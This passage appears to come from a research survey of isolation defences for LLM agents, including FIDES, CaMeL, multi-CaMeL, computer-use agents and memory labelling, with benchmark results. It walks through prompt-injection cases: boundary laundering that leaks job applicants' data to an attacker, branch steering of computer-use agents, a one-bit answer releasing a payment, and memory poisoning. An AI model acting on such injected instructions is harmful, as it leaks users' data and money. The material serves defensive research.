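Costa and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's 97 user tasks by hand and classed 20 as data-dependent. These make up only 5% of the Workspace tasks and 10% of the Travel tasks, but 43.8% of the Banking tasks and 42.9% of the Slack tasks. Another 51 tasks are data-independent but need a quarantined model to process some text, for example to summarise it. The remaining 26 only involve passing values between tools. An agent that never looks at untrusted data will therefore do much better on a benchmark made up mostly of office tasks than on one about paying bills.

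An agent can also complete a data-dependent task by guessing. One banking task is to change the user's password if there has been a suspicious transaction. When Costa and colleagues ran FIDES on it, the privileged model had access to the amounts and dates, which counted as trusted, but not the descriptions. It treated a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without reading what the payment was for. This broke no policy, but an agent that works this way will sometimes change the password unnecessarily.

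### Letting a short answer through

The narrowest way to let data influence a plan is a yes/no answer. Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to read the top three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. FIDES can handle it as follows:

1. The privileged model requests the emails, and the software stores their text in hidden variables.
2. The privileged model has the quarantined model check the emails for a meeting request and restricts the answer to true or false.
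3. The privileged model looks at that answer. If it is false, the task is finished.
4. If it is true, the privileged model has the quarantined model extract the details of the event into fixed fields. The software stores the result in another hidden variable.
5. The privileged model calls the calendar tool with that variable's name.

The privileged model learns that somebody wants a meeting, but not who or when.

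A fixed list of options lets a little more information through. For example, the quarantined model could choose between scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding the email, and the privileged model would then plan the steps for that choice. A schema, which specifies an answer's fields and their types, can also let through dates, numbers and addresses.

Software can enforce these formats with constrained decoding. Before the quarantined model produces each token, the software rules out every token that would break the format.

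FIDES can add the answer's type to its label. The types have an order based on how much information they can carry:

true/false ⊑ choice from a fixed list ⊑ free text

A policy can then let an untrusted yes/no answer, but not untrusted free text, influence an action. Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their AgentDojo tests because they found it unnecessary for most of the tasks, so their results don't show how effective typed answers are in practice.

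If the privileged model needs more than a typed answer, FIDES lets it read the whole hidden value. This makes the model's context untrusted, so it can no longer take sensitive actions. That is enough for a user who only wants a question answered, but it doesn't help with a TODO list whose items require payments or messages.

#### How much an answer can carry

One choice among *n* options carries at most log₂(*n*) bits of information, so a yes/no answer carries at most 1 bit and a choice among eight options at most 3 bits. A series of *k* choices, each among *n* options, carries at most *k* × log₂(*n*) bits.

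If an agent sorts each item on a ten-item TODO list into one of eight kinds of task, its answers can carry 30 bits, enough to select any one of about a billion (2³⁰) sequences of tasks. An attacker who controls the whole list can choose the sequence, but only from the kinds of task that the privileged model offered.

The answers to repeated questions can also let through text that a single answer could not. Five yes/no questions are enough to identify a letter of the alphabet, since they can distinguish 2⁵ = 32 possibilities. A privileged model that kept asking about a hidden sentence could spell it out, along with any injection it contained. A designer therefore has to limit the number of questions as well as the size of each answer.

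### One bit can release a payment

The number of bits limits how many different messages an attacker can send, but it doesn't limit the damage that one of them can do. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a builder $5,000 once an email confirms that the work is finished. The plan might be:

```
email = read_latest_email(sender="builder@example.com")
finished = ask_quarantined_model("Is the work finished?", email, type=yes_no)
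if finished == "yes":
    send_money(recipient=builder_account, amount=5000)
```

The user supplied the account and the amount, so both are trusted. The email contributes one bit, which decides whether $5,000 leaves the user's account.

The builder could get the money early by lying about the work, which might also fool a human assistant. A language model could also be fooled by an email that says the work is half done but carries a hidden instruction to answer "yes". *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) proposes a property called judgment integrity, which requires an agent's decision to depend only on the task-relevant parts of the untrusted data. The hidden instruction violates this property, but the lie doesn't. Restricting the answer's type can't enforce judgment integrity, because "yes" is a valid answer in both cases.

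Costa and colleagues argue that a policy can reasonably accept a yes/no answer because one is unlikely to lead to a prompt injection. Seip, Markovinović and Hein (2026), in *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use*, reply that one bit can be enough to steer the privileged model into a harmful branch. Both claims are right, but they concern different harms. One bit can't tell the privileged model to forward the mailbox, but it can trigger a payment that the plan already includes. A designer should therefore consider how much harm the worst permitted answer could do, as well as how many answers are permitted. Choosing among eight folders for an email conveys three bits but risks very little.

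Garby and colleagues object that exceptions for small values are hard to audit. When FIDES accepts a yes/no answer under such a policy, a reviewer of that run can't tell whether the answer was legitimate or the result of an attack. In their own language, a program has to endorse an untrusted value explicitly before treating it as trusted. A reviewer can then search the program for every endorsement, though an endorsement can still be a mistake.

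Under CaMeL's strict mode, a policy could block the payment because an untrusted email had influenced it, but the same policy would also block the payment when the work really was finished.

### Asking the user to trust the data

The system can also let the user decide. Kolluri and colleagues built Prudentia, an agent based on FIDES, which can do this in two ways. The survey *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) describes these as permission to trust data and approval to perform an action.

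Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email containing a TODO list of ten items, each of which requires a sensitive tool call. If the agent reads the email without permission, its context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve each of the ten calls. If the user endorses the email first, the agent can read it in a trusted context and carry out all ten items after asking the user only once.

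The single question is more convenient, but it covers everything in the email. If an attacker has added an eleventh item, the agent will carry it out too, so the user has to read the whole text carefully before agreeing. Separate approvals let the user see each action and its arguments just before it happens. Endorsement seems better suited to a short list from a colleague than to a long document from a stranger.

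Prudentia can also read a hidden value without asking the user, which makes sense when no sensitive action will follow. It must first state why it needs to read the value and which tool calls it expects to make afterwards. Kolluri and colleagues decided against a similar general permission to release private data, because whether a release is appropriate depends so much on the situation. The user still approves each call that would release private data.

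The Prudentia paper proposes two measures of how often an agent interrupts its user. The first is the total number of interventions across the tasks it completes. The second is the share of tasks it completes with at most *k* interventions each, so *k* = 0 gives the share it completes alone. Compared with FIDES on AgentDojo, Prudentia completed up to 9% more tasks alone and reduced interventions by a factor of up to 1.9. On WASP, a set of web tasks that are all data-independent, it needed no interventions.

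These tests involved no attacks, and the researchers assumed that the user would approve every request in a successful task. The measures therefore show how often the agent interrupts the user, but not whether a real user would notice a bad request. Users may answer more carefully when an agent asks less often, but Kolluri and colleagues didn't test this.

*APPA* (2026) tries to avoid both the questions and the loss of trust by having the agent inspect untrusted data in a confined side run, which keeps the main context clean. It reports that no attacks succeeded in 1,320 protected test runs under the policies it tested, and that the agent completed between 64.2% and 91% of tasks. The main run still needs some result from the inspection to act on the data, so a designer has to decide what the side run may return.

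### Writing every branch in advance

A computer-use agent, which operates a computer through its screen, seems very poorly suited to isolation. It normally receives a screenshot, chooses a click or keystroke, and receives another screenshot. Any of these images may contain text from an advertiser or a stranger on a forum, but an agent that can't see the screen would seem unable to do anything.

In January 2026, Foerster and colleagues showed that a planner can complete many such tasks without seeing the screen. In their adaptation of CaMeL, the privileged model writes a program that has to cover in advance whatever the agent may encounter. This is possible because much of what appears on a screen is predictable. For example, a browser is either open or closed, and a website may or may not show a cookie notice.

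The researchers told the planner to build its programs from a routine with three parts:

- **Observe:** a quarantined vision model describes the screen, or a tool lists the elements of the page.
- **Verify:** a quarantined model compares that description with a condition in the plan, such as "a cookie notice is visible", and reports whether it holds.
- **Act:** the interpreter follows the branch for that result and clicks or types, using screen positions supplied by the vision model.

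The planner never receives the descriptions or the results. The interpreter uses them to choose among branches that the planner has already written.

In one example, the user asks the agent to browse a natural products database, and the browser is already open at a website about medicines. The task description doesn't mention the website, so the plan has separate branches for an open website, an empty search page and the desktop. If a website is open, the agent looks for the site's search box, trying several descriptions of it in case the vision model misses it the first time. It then checks whether the results are relevant and, if they aren't, searches the wider web.

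These plans are much longer than the ones CaMeL writes for AgentDojo, where tools return structured data:

| Average per plan | AgentDojo | Computer use, without the routine | Computer use, with the routine |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 19.8 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 11.3 | 39.7 |
| Lines of code | 51.8 | 71.6 | 213.3 |

In the longest plans, roughly half of the steps are fallbacks that don't run, but they are still useful. On one set of 60 tasks, with up to three attempts at each, the agent completed 35 with the routine and 11 without it.

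#### The same routine in FIDES

Foerster and colleagues also built a version on FIDES, which calls the planner before each step. FIDES normally hides the results of checks from the planner, so the planner can't choose a branch. The researchers therefore let it see yes/no answers. A planner could eventually learn everything on the screen by asking enough questions, so they set limits of 70 function calls per task and five uses of any one variable. Seventy yes/no answers carry at most 70 bits, which is less than nine characters of text at eight bits each.

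On the set of 60 tasks, the FIDES version completed 20 on the first attempt and 40 within five attempts, while the CaMeL version completed 25 and 39. The CaMeL version used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent, and the FIDES version used 29.6 times as many because it resent the full history to the planner at every step. For 17 tasks, the CaMeL version cost $5.40 and the FIDES version cost $76.07, excluding the main vision model, which ran on the researchers' own machines. The defended versions had up to five attempts at each of these tasks, so the token multiples cover more than a single run.

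### What the 57% figure measures

The researchers tested their agents on OSWorld, a benchmark of 369 tasks in real desktop applications such as Chrome and LibreOffice. Scripts can check 339 of the tasks, and the other 30 count as successes by default. Their main result is that isolation retains up to 57% of the performance of frontier models.

That figure comes from Foerster and colleagues' test of Claude Sonnet 4.5 as the vision model. Claude completed 31 of 109 tasks (28.4%) on the first attempt and 62 (56.9%) within five. The 109 tasks are the ones Claude had already completed without the defence, in one attempt of at most 15 steps. The undefended agent therefore scores 100% on this set, and 57% is the share of its successes that the defended agent could repeat.

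They chose the sets for two smaller open models in the same way:

| Vision model | Tasks it had completed undefended | Completed with isolation, first attempt | Completed with isolation, within five attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B | 60 | 25 (41.7%) | 39 (65.0%) |
| OpenCUA-32B | 76 | 22 (28.9%) | 48 (63.2%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 31 (28.4%) | 62 (56.9%) |

This way of choosing tasks is a little unfair to the defended agent, because the undefended agent may have completed some of them by luck, and the set leaves out any task that only the defended agent could do. But the defended agent had five attempts, while the undefended agent had only one.

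Counting the best of five attempts also assumes that something can pick out the successful one, which is why Foerster and colleagues describe the result as an upper bound. A user who wants a slide reformatted can throw away four bad versions, but if the task is to send an email, a failed first attempt may already have reached the wrong person.

The study also reports an improvement of up to 19% for smaller models, but the agents compared again had different numbers of attempts. UI-TARS alone scored 24.4% on OSWorld with one attempt, and the defended agent that used it scored 29.0% with three. When each had one attempt at the 339 tasks that scripts can check, the undefended agent completed 60 and the defended agent completed 51.

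On the same 60 tasks, all three vision models completed between 65.0% and 68.3% within five attempts, so the choice of vision model made little difference. The choice of planner mattered more, since among nine planners tested on 17 tasks, GPT-5 completed 12 and the two weakest completed four each.

Foerster and colleagues conclude that computer tasks are often less data-dependent than they appear. Their results support this for tasks like changing a setting or finding a page, where a planner can predict the main possibilities, such as a cookie notice. They acknowledge that the approach can't handle a task whose sequence of actions appears only in the untrusted data. For example, a planner can't write a branch for every item that somebody might add to a TODO list.

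### Branch steering

A plan with many branches gives an attacker many decisions to influence. Foerster and colleagues use the term branch steering for an attack in which false observations make the agent follow a harmful branch already in its plan. Suppose the plan includes a branch for dismissing a cookie notice if one appears. If the vision model wrongly detects a notice, the agent enters that branch and clicks the location the model gives, which may take it to a malicious website even though it has followed its plan exactly.

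The researchers tried to catch false observations with two checks, each tested against a different attack. One compared the vision model's answer with the underlying structure of the page. It flagged six of ten attacked runs and raised false alarms on four of 17 harmless tasks. The other had an independent model review the screenshot and the answer. It flagged five of ten attacked runs and raised false alarms on three of the 17 harmless tasks. A further attack got past both kinds of check. Running both checks raised the token count from 1.88 to 6.57 times that of the undefended agent, a large increase for catching about half the attacks.

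Foerster and colleagues reply that control-flow integrity still secures a good deal. Since an attacker can't add actions, more serious harm needs a more convenient plan:

- To send the agent to a hostile website, the attacker needs one false answer about something most plans look for.
- To steal money, the attacker needs a plan that already makes a transfer, an agent that is logged in at the right moment, and at least two false answers that fit together, for example about the recipient field and the confirm button.
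- To steal data, the attacker needs a plan that reads something and later sends something, and has to corrupt both steps.

They add that the user can approve the complete plan before the agent does anything.

This reply is convincing for an agent that looks things up, but less so for one that pays bills, because every plan for paying a bill includes a transfer. The guarantee is also weaker when an agent clicks on a screen than when it calls named tools. A call to `read_calendar` can only read the calendar, but a click can have almost any effect, depending on what is under the cursor. Foerster and colleagues ran their agents without CaMeL's data policies partly for this reason, since a rule about clicks would apply equally to a harmless click and a payment.

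### Checking a value against another source

Seip and colleagues propose a computer-use agent, SA-CUA, that can see part of the screen and can endorse some values without asking the user. The software masks the whole screen, then uncovers the parts that only the site's operator or the application can change, such as menus and toolbars. The privileged model plans from this partial view, and the software blocks any click in a masked area.

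To use a value from a masked area, the agent has to verify it against a source the attacker doesn't control. Seip and colleagues give the example of a user who wants a Python package that prints coloured text in the terminal. The agent finds a recommendation in a forum post, which anyone could have written. It could check the name like this:

1. The quarantined model extracts the package name, and the software hides it from the privileged model.
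2. The privileged model, without seeing that name, uses its own knowledge to say which package or packages would fit the user's description.
3. Ordinary software compares the hidden name with that answer.
4. If they match, the software relabels the name as trusted and shows it to the privileged model.

If the post recommends `termcolor`, a real package for this purpose, the check can succeed. If it recommends an attacker's package, the name doesn't match and the agent can't install it. The attacker can make the check fail, but can't make it accept a name they chose. Security researchers call this robust endorsement, because the value being checked can't influence the test. Asking another model whether the name looks right would not be robust, since the name could contain text that manipulates the model's answer.

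The agent has to check other values against other sources, such as an email address against the user's contacts or a filename against a list of trusted files. The method fails when no independent source exists. In one such case, the researchers made an exception to their own rule because many tasks would otherwise have been impossible. They let the agent treat GitHub as an authority on which repository is genuine, although outsiders write much of GitHub's content.

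They compared SA-CUA with an undefended agent and with the CaMeL version by Foerster and colleagues, which they ran again in their own setup. With Qwen3.8-27B as the planner, the agents completed these shares of the user's tasks:

| Tasks | Undefended | CaMeL version | SA-CUA |
|---|---|---|---|
| 65 tasks with hostile instructions mixed into text the agent needs | 95.4% | 18.5% | 86.2% |
| 78 tasks with a false value of the right type | 53.4% | 18.8% | 50.9% |
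| 36 OSWorld tasks with no attack | 58.3% | 8.3% | 30.6% |

The second row gives results for false values, which typed answers can't stop. Against the undefended agent, attacks succeeded in at least one of three runs on 46.2% of the tasks in the first row and 43.6% in the second. Neither isolated agent carried out any attack. In the second row, this is weak evidence that the CaMeL version is secure, because it failed to complete 81.2% of those runs. SA-CUA failed to complete 49.1% of them, but it completed nearly as many as the undefended agent.

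The 8.3% in the last row doesn't contradict the 57% that Foerster and colleagues reported. Seip and colleagues used a different planner and a small subset of OSWorld that wasn't limited to tasks the undefended agent had already completed.

SA-CUA protects against manipulation but not against leaks, so it could still post private information in public. It also turns down some requests, because a classifier checks before each task whether the user has described the required values precisely enough for the agent to verify them. A request to "follow the instructions on screen" fails this test, and the agent asks the user to be more specific. A request to complete whatever is on a shared TODO list would presumably fail for the same reason.

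Being specific doesn't always help. Seip and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to find and buy a laptop that meets a certain condition. Often the only evidence that a laptop meets the condition is the seller's description, and SA-CUA has nothing to compare it with. The agent can report what the seller claims, but the user has to decide whether to believe it before the agent buys the laptop.

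## Does isolation hold when agents pass work to each other?

So far, this report has covered a single agent working for a person. Many systems now divide the work among several agents, so one agent's output becomes another's input. In October 2026, Peters-Gill and colleagues found that an injection can take control of such a system even when every agent runs CaMeL.

### When an agent's user is another agent

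In the systems studied, a coordinating agent called the orchestrator takes the user's request and gives parts of it to specialised agents. It calls each specialist like a tool, sending text and waiting for a reply. The specialist trusts that text because it treats the orchestrator as its user. The agents form a tree in which each specialist has one caller and only the orchestrator communicates with the human user.

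*Architecture Matters for Multi-Agent Security* (2026) describes how Inspect, a widely used test framework, starts a specialist with a fresh context in which the only user message is the text the orchestrator wrote. Unless the orchestrator copies in the person's original request, the specialist can't compare its instructions with what the person wanted.

A2A, Google's protocol for messages between agents, gives each message the role "user" or "agent". According to the documentation of Agno, which makes agent software, "user" means the client, the program that sent the request. A request written by an agent therefore has the same role as one typed by a person, even if part of it came from a web page.

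### The job applicants

In the main example, a user asks an orchestrator to send Julie a Slack message summarising all job applicants. The orchestrator can call a database agent and a notification agent, the second of which can post on Slack and send email. All three run CaMeL without data policies, with GPT-5.2 as both the privileged and the quarantined model. An attacker has planted an instruction in the database to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

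1. The orchestrator's privileged model reads the user's request and writes a program. The program gets the records from the database agent, has the quarantined model summarise them, and asks the notification agent to send the summary.
2. The database agent's privileged model reads a request for the records and writes a program with one query. The result goes into a variable that this model never reads.
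3. The orchestrator's program stores the reply in another variable and has the quarantined model summarise it. The attacker's instruction survives in the summary.
4. The program inserts the summary into a sentence that tells the notification agent to send it to Julie.
5. The notification agent receives the whole sentence as its user's request. Its privileged model reads the attacker's instruction along with the rest, and writes a program that posts the summary on Slack and also emails it to the attacker.

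The orchestrator and the database agent write the same programs whether or not the injection is present. The notification agent also follows its program exactly, but it wrote that program after reading the attacker's text. The text changed from untrusted data to a trusted instruction at step 4. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering, meaning that data one agent treats as untrusted reaches another agent as trusted input. Willison had warned against returning a free-text summary to the privileged model, and here the summary reaches a privileged model in a different agent.

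Isolating each agent still stops attacks that depend on controlling the agent that reads the data. In an earlier attack called OMNI-Leak, text in a public database makes the database agent open a private database. With CaMeL in every agent, this attack failed in all five trials, and the system still answered every legitimate query.

### How general is the failure?

Peters-Gill and colleagues also prove a general result. A tree of two or more agents lacks control-flow integrity whenever at least one tool returns untrusted data, even if each agent has that property on its own. The proof makes two assumptions about what users can request:

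- For any tool an agent has, some request makes the agent call the tool and return its result.
- For any two tools an agent has, some request makes the agent call one and then call the other with arguments that depend on the first result. Specialists count as tools here, and the agent may call the same tool twice.

If any agent in a multi-agent system has a tool that returns untrusted data, some requests will make a privileged model plan its actions from untrusted text. If the agent with the tool can call a specialist, some request will make it read the data and use them in its instruction to that specialist. If it has no specialists, another agent must call it, and some request will make that caller get the data from it and then call it again with an instruction based on the reply. This can happen even in a system with one orchestrator and one specialist.

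The paper's assumptions are mild, as it claims, for a general assistant. An ordinary request such as "Read the complaint and ask the refunds agent to deal with it" meets the harder of the two. The assumptions don't hold for a system that only runs fixed jobs, such as a nightly report for which developers have written every message between agents. They may hold if a specialist agent accepts only a choice from a short list of instructions, but the attacker gains little because the developer can check every instruction in advance.

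The proof shows that at least one request exposes the system, but not how many do. The harm also depends on which tools are available to the agent that receives the injected instruction. An injection can't make an agent send email if the agent's only tool reads a calendar.

### Separate channels for instructions and data

The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each call between agents into a message and a set of variables. The receiving agent's privileged model reads the message, but it knows the variables only by name. In the job applicant example, the orchestrator's last step would look roughly like this:

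```
notification_agent(
    message="Send the text in 'summary' to Julie on Slack.",
    variables={"summary": summary}
)
```

The notification agent's privileged model plans one Slack message from this instruction. The resulting program fetches the summary only when it runs, so an injection in the summary can't add an email to the plan. Julie may still receive a strange or false summary.

The system tells the orchestrator's model to put anything from a tool in the variables, but security doesn't depend on the model obeying. The interpreter that runs its program enforces two rules:

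- The message may not depend on the output of any tool.
- Values keep their labels when they pass from one agent to another.

The rule about messages gives the whole system control-flow integrity. Each agent plans from an instruction that contains no tool output, so the user's request and other trusted information determine every plan. In principle, replacing each call to a specialist with the specialist's own program would produce a single large program. Untrusted data can still affect which of that program's branches run, but it can't add new ones.

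Preserved labels let a data policy work across agents. For example, the notification agent's mail tool could check who may read the applicants' records. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran all their tests without data policies, so their results don't show how well such policies work across agents.

Multi-CaMeL relies more on label tracking than CaMeL does. If CaMeL's interpreter loses a label, the data policies may fail but the plan stays fixed. In multi-CaMeL, a lost label can let untrusted text into another agent's instructions. The implementation inherits CaMeL's problem with branches that a program skips, as the paper acknowledges. Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL's interpreter could treat an untrusted value as trusted once a program inserted it into a piece of text. That fault would be serious if multi-CaMeL inherited it, because boundary laundering works this way.

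### Attacks on MultiAgentDojo

To measure the effect, the researchers built MultiAgentDojo, which divides the tools in each AgentDojo suite among two to four specialist agents under an orchestrator. In Workspace, for example, separate agents handle email, the calendar and the cloud drive. MultiAgentDojo keeps the original user tasks and attack goals. Without isolation, the five models tested completed about as many tasks on average as on the original benchmark.

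Each model faced 949 attacked instances in each of three settings, with these attack success rates:

| Model | No isolation | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 12.9% | 0.2% | 0.0% |

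With CaMeL in each agent, only about nine of 4,745 attacks succeeded, all through boundary laundering. That is too few to measure precisely how much multi-CaMeL adds, and its design is better evidence that it closes the gap. The low rate may also make the separate CaMeL agents look safer than they are. AgentDojo's attacks were written for a single agent, and an attacker who knew the system could write text intended to survive a summary and influence the next agent. Peters-Gill and colleagues similarly warn that GPT-5.5 may have scored zero without any isolation only because the benchmark's attacks are too weak.

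One of the successful attacks occurred during a task to visit two people's websites and send them feedback. With CaMeL in each agent, Gemini 2.5 Pro wrote a plan that pasted a page's text into the instruction to the Slack agent, which then sent the attacker's link to a third person. The paper contrasts this with a multi-CaMeL run that faced a different injection on the same task. That attack failed, and the system completed the task.

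In the multi-CaMeL run, however, the privileged model made up the feedback and wrote it into the plan, including compliments on the design of websites it couldn't see. The plan could have had the quarantined model write the feedback from the pages. The paper still describes the task as completed, so a successful run doesn't always mean the user got what they asked for.

### How many tasks still get done?

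The researchers also used AssetOpsBench, a set of 141 tasks about maintaining industrial equipment. They excluded 29 tasks because the necessary data didn't exist. One task is to list the sensors on a cooling machine that could help detect an overheating compressor. One agent lists all the machine's sensors, and the orchestrator passes the list as a variable to a second agent, which picks out the relevant ones. The test included no attacks, and a language model judged the answers.

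These are the shares of tasks completed without attacks on both benchmarks:

| Model | AssetOpsBench, no isolation | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL | MultiAgentDojo, no isolation | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% | 67.0% | 67.9% | 69.1% | 53.6% | 52.6% |
| GPT-5.5 | 87.5% | 82.1% | 79.5% | 86.6% | 73.2% | 66.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.2% | 64.3% | 48.2% | 78.4% | 38.1% | 24.7% |
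| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9% | 55.4% | 50.9% | 76.3% | 42.3% | 26.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 64.3% | 20.5% | 26.8% | 27.8% | 13.4% | 7.2% |

Running CaMeL in each agent lowers scores on AssetOpsBench by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL lowers them by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, these drops average 13.4 and 0.85 points. Peters-Gill and colleagues call the additional loss from multi-CaMeL modest, which seems fair for AssetOpsBench. On MultiAgentDojo, however, the additional loss averages 8.7 points, and GPT-4.1 completes less than a third as many tasks with multi-CaMeL as without isolation.

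Isolation generally costs stronger models a smaller share of the tasks they could complete without it. On MultiAgentDojo, GPT-5.5 and Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite both drop 20.6 percentage points when multi-CaMeL is added. That is about a quarter of the tasks GPT-5.5 completed without isolation and three quarters of those Flash Lite completed. The trend is uneven and based on only five models.

Fable 5's scores are hard to interpret because the model refused many harmless MultiAgentDojo tasks, perhaps because the environment resembled a known security test. The paper reports that it refused 52 of the 97 tasks. It can't have refused all 52 without isolation, because it completed 67 tasks in that setting, so the count probably includes every task it refused in at least one setting. On the remaining 45 tasks, it completed 91.1% without isolation and 84.4% with either version of CaMeL, a much smaller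 loss than the table shows.

Most failures in both versions of CaMeL happened because a plan didn't allow for something an agent learned only while carrying it out. In several AssetOpsBench runs, a specialist couldn't find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for a similar machine or period instead. The orchestrator's fixed program then used those data as if they were correct.

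### Carrying labels between suppliers

Multi-CaMeL works when one developer controls all the agents. When agents and tools come from different suppliers, they need a shared way to send labels. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a prototype that puts labels in an existing metadata field of MCP messages. Tool calls carry labels for the decision to make the call and for its arguments, as in FIDES, and tools return labels with their results. Software that doesn't support the labels can ignore them and still work.

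These labels aren't yet part of the MCP standard. In March 2026 the standard's blog, Model Context Protocol (2026), listed a proposal for trust and sensitivity labels as a draft. The existing annotations, such as whether a tool only reads data, are hints that clients must distrust unless they trust the supplier. Labels have the same problem, since a malicious supplier could mark an attacker's text as trusted.

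When a tool has no labels, Microsoft suggests inferring them cautiously. The software assumes that anything sent to the tool may appear in its result, and treats results from tools that reach the outside world as untrusted. Receivers also need a rule for unknown labels. *SafeFlow* (2026), which labels data across workflows with several agents, rejects any output with an unknown label and holds back dangerous actions that depend on it.

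In *Language-Based Agent Control*, a specialist that reads untrusted text can keep its tools, and labels restrict which calls it may make after reading. This suits a specialist that has to look up one thing after another, but the labels can spread until they block legitimate work.

Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated this spread without running any language models. In the simulation, an agent that read or passed on sensitive data kept the sensitive label for the rest of the task. They measured the share of tool calls that were affected, meaning that the calls introduced sensitive data or ran under that label. In one test, five agents made 20 tool calls, of which four introduced sensitive data. The affected share was about 5 percentage points higher when an orchestrator relayed everything than when the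 agents communicated directly.

Adding agents reduced the spread because each one handled less of the data. Giving the sensitive tools to only a few agents also helped. But more agents can mean many more connections to monitor. If every pair communicates directly, five agents have 10 connections and 20 agents have 190. No arrangement stopped the spread completely, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that systems also need safe ways to remove labels. Their simulation assumes that an agent takes on the label of anything it relays. But a multi-CaMeL orchestrator passes on values its privileged model can't see, so that model's context could keep its trusted label.

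### Files and memories that agents share

Agents can also pass information without a call, by writing to a file that another agent reads later. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) gives the example of one agent that copies a secret into a file and another that sends the file out. Checking each agent separately can miss the leak, because the first agent sends nothing out and the second never opens the original secret. The proposed system records the labels on shared files, so the second agent's software can detect that the file contains a secret.

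Long-term memory is harder to label because agents often have a model summarise what they've seen before storing it. *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (Xu, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) describes a web page that recommends a workflow for setting up monitoring. The model stores this as the user's usual workflow. In a later task, the agent follows the recommendation because it appears to come from the user. The stored note contains no obvious injection for a filter to find, and the model has removed the evidence that the recommendation came from an outside web page.

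This attack succeeded in 93.3% of invented test cases when the small open model Qwen2.5-14B wrote the memories. A content filter reduced this to 20% but had no effect on a second set of cases designed to be harder to detect. Xu and colleagues propose a defence in which ordinary software records the source of each memory, and each claim in a memory gets no more authority than the claim's least trusted source. A memory from a web page can still help the agent find information, but it can't authorise a purchase unless the user has confirmed it. No unauthorised high-risk action got through in their tests, which assumed the recorded sources were correct.

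*Utility Under Attack* (2026) also labels each memory by the channel it came through and treats anything written by another agent as untrusted. Untrusted memories may still be accurate, so discarding them all would make shared memory nearly useless.

*PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) lets agents use untrusted memories after confirmation. The agent that acts sees only a name for each untrusted memory, while a quarantined model searches the contents. Before the agent can read a memory or pass it to a sensitive tool, a person or another model must confirm the exact text. The researchers used Lean to check a proof that, for a single user's memory, hidden text can affect the agent only through what the confirmation step displays. A confirmation covers a particular value and tool but isn't tied to a task or a time, so an account number approved for one payment remains approved for later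 ones.

PerMIT also lets users and agents share their confirmations. Once enough of them have confirmed an item, everyone else can use it without checking it. In tests with up to 90 autonomous agents, no direct injection got enough confirmations to skip checking, and the shared knowledge helped new agents with customer-service tasks they hadn't seen before. Jiang and colleagues prove that the risk of accepting a poisoned item falls as the community grows, under assumptions about how accurate the checkers are and how many identities an attacker controls. But if most of the checkers run the same model, a text that fools one may well fool the others.

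## What does isolation cost in completed tasks, time and money?

With isolation, an agent can't complete tasks that depend on information the design hides from the privileged model, or tasks that need a tool call a policy blocks. The tasks it does complete usually take more computation, and therefore more time and money. Developers also have to label data, write policies and describe what each tool returns. A better model reduces some of these problems, but it can't complete a task that needs a forbidden call.

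### What FIDES loses, and why

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks and averaged five runs. They compared it with an ordinary agent loop, which they call the basic planner, and ran each with and without policies. They used GPT-4o and o1, two OpenAI models from 2024, so the results may not hold for current models.

With policies on, the paper says, FIDES completed 8% more tasks than the basic planner using GPT-4o and 16% more using o1. With policies off, FIDES completed 6.3% fewer using o1. All three figures are percentage points, as the average scores across the four suites show:

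| Agent | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic planner, policies off | 84.3% | 84.0% |
| FIDES, policies off | 60.6% | 77.6% |
| FIDES, policies on | 50.0% | 60.8% |
| Basic planner, policies on | 41.9% | 44.4% |

These averages give each suite the same weight, although Workspace has 40 tasks and Banking has 16. If each task has the same weight instead, the 8-point gain becomes about 11 points.

The 6.3-point loss understates the effect of adopting FIDES because it leaves out the policies, which FIDES needs to be secure. With GPT-4o and no policies, 21 attacks still succeeded, compared with 152 against the basic planner. For someone deciding whether to adopt FIDES, the better comparison is between the first and third rows of the table, which shows a loss of 34 points with GPT-4o and 23 with o1.

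The main cause of the loss differed between the two models. With GPT-4o, hiding data from the planner accounted for 24 points and the policies for another 11. With o1, hiding data accounted for only 6 points and the policies for 17. o1, the stronger model, was much better at working with variables it couldn't read. The policies probably caused a larger loss with o1 because GPT-4o had already failed many of the tasks they would have blocked.

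Some of GPT-4o's failures were plain mistakes, such as mixing up variable names. In one Slack task, it listed all the channels although the user had already named the right one, which made its context untrusted unnecessarily. In the Travel suite, FIDES with policies completed 41% of tasks, compared with 73% for the basic planner with the same policies. The policies allow many travel tools to run in an untrusted context, so hiding data had little benefit.

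Utility scores can also overstate what a design can do. Costa and colleagues tested the simpler planner, which passes variables to tools but can't read what the variables contain. They classified none of the 20 Travel tasks as suited to this planner, yet it completed 43% of them with GPT-4o. In some cases it recommended a hotel without seeing any ratings and happened to pick a good one. With o1, it completed 2% of the tasks.

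### CaMeL and the LLMbda agent on banking tasks

Garby and colleagues ran their LLMbda agent three times on each of the 16 tasks in AgentDojo's Banking suite. Its label checks were always on. They also reran CaMeL with two of the same models:

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
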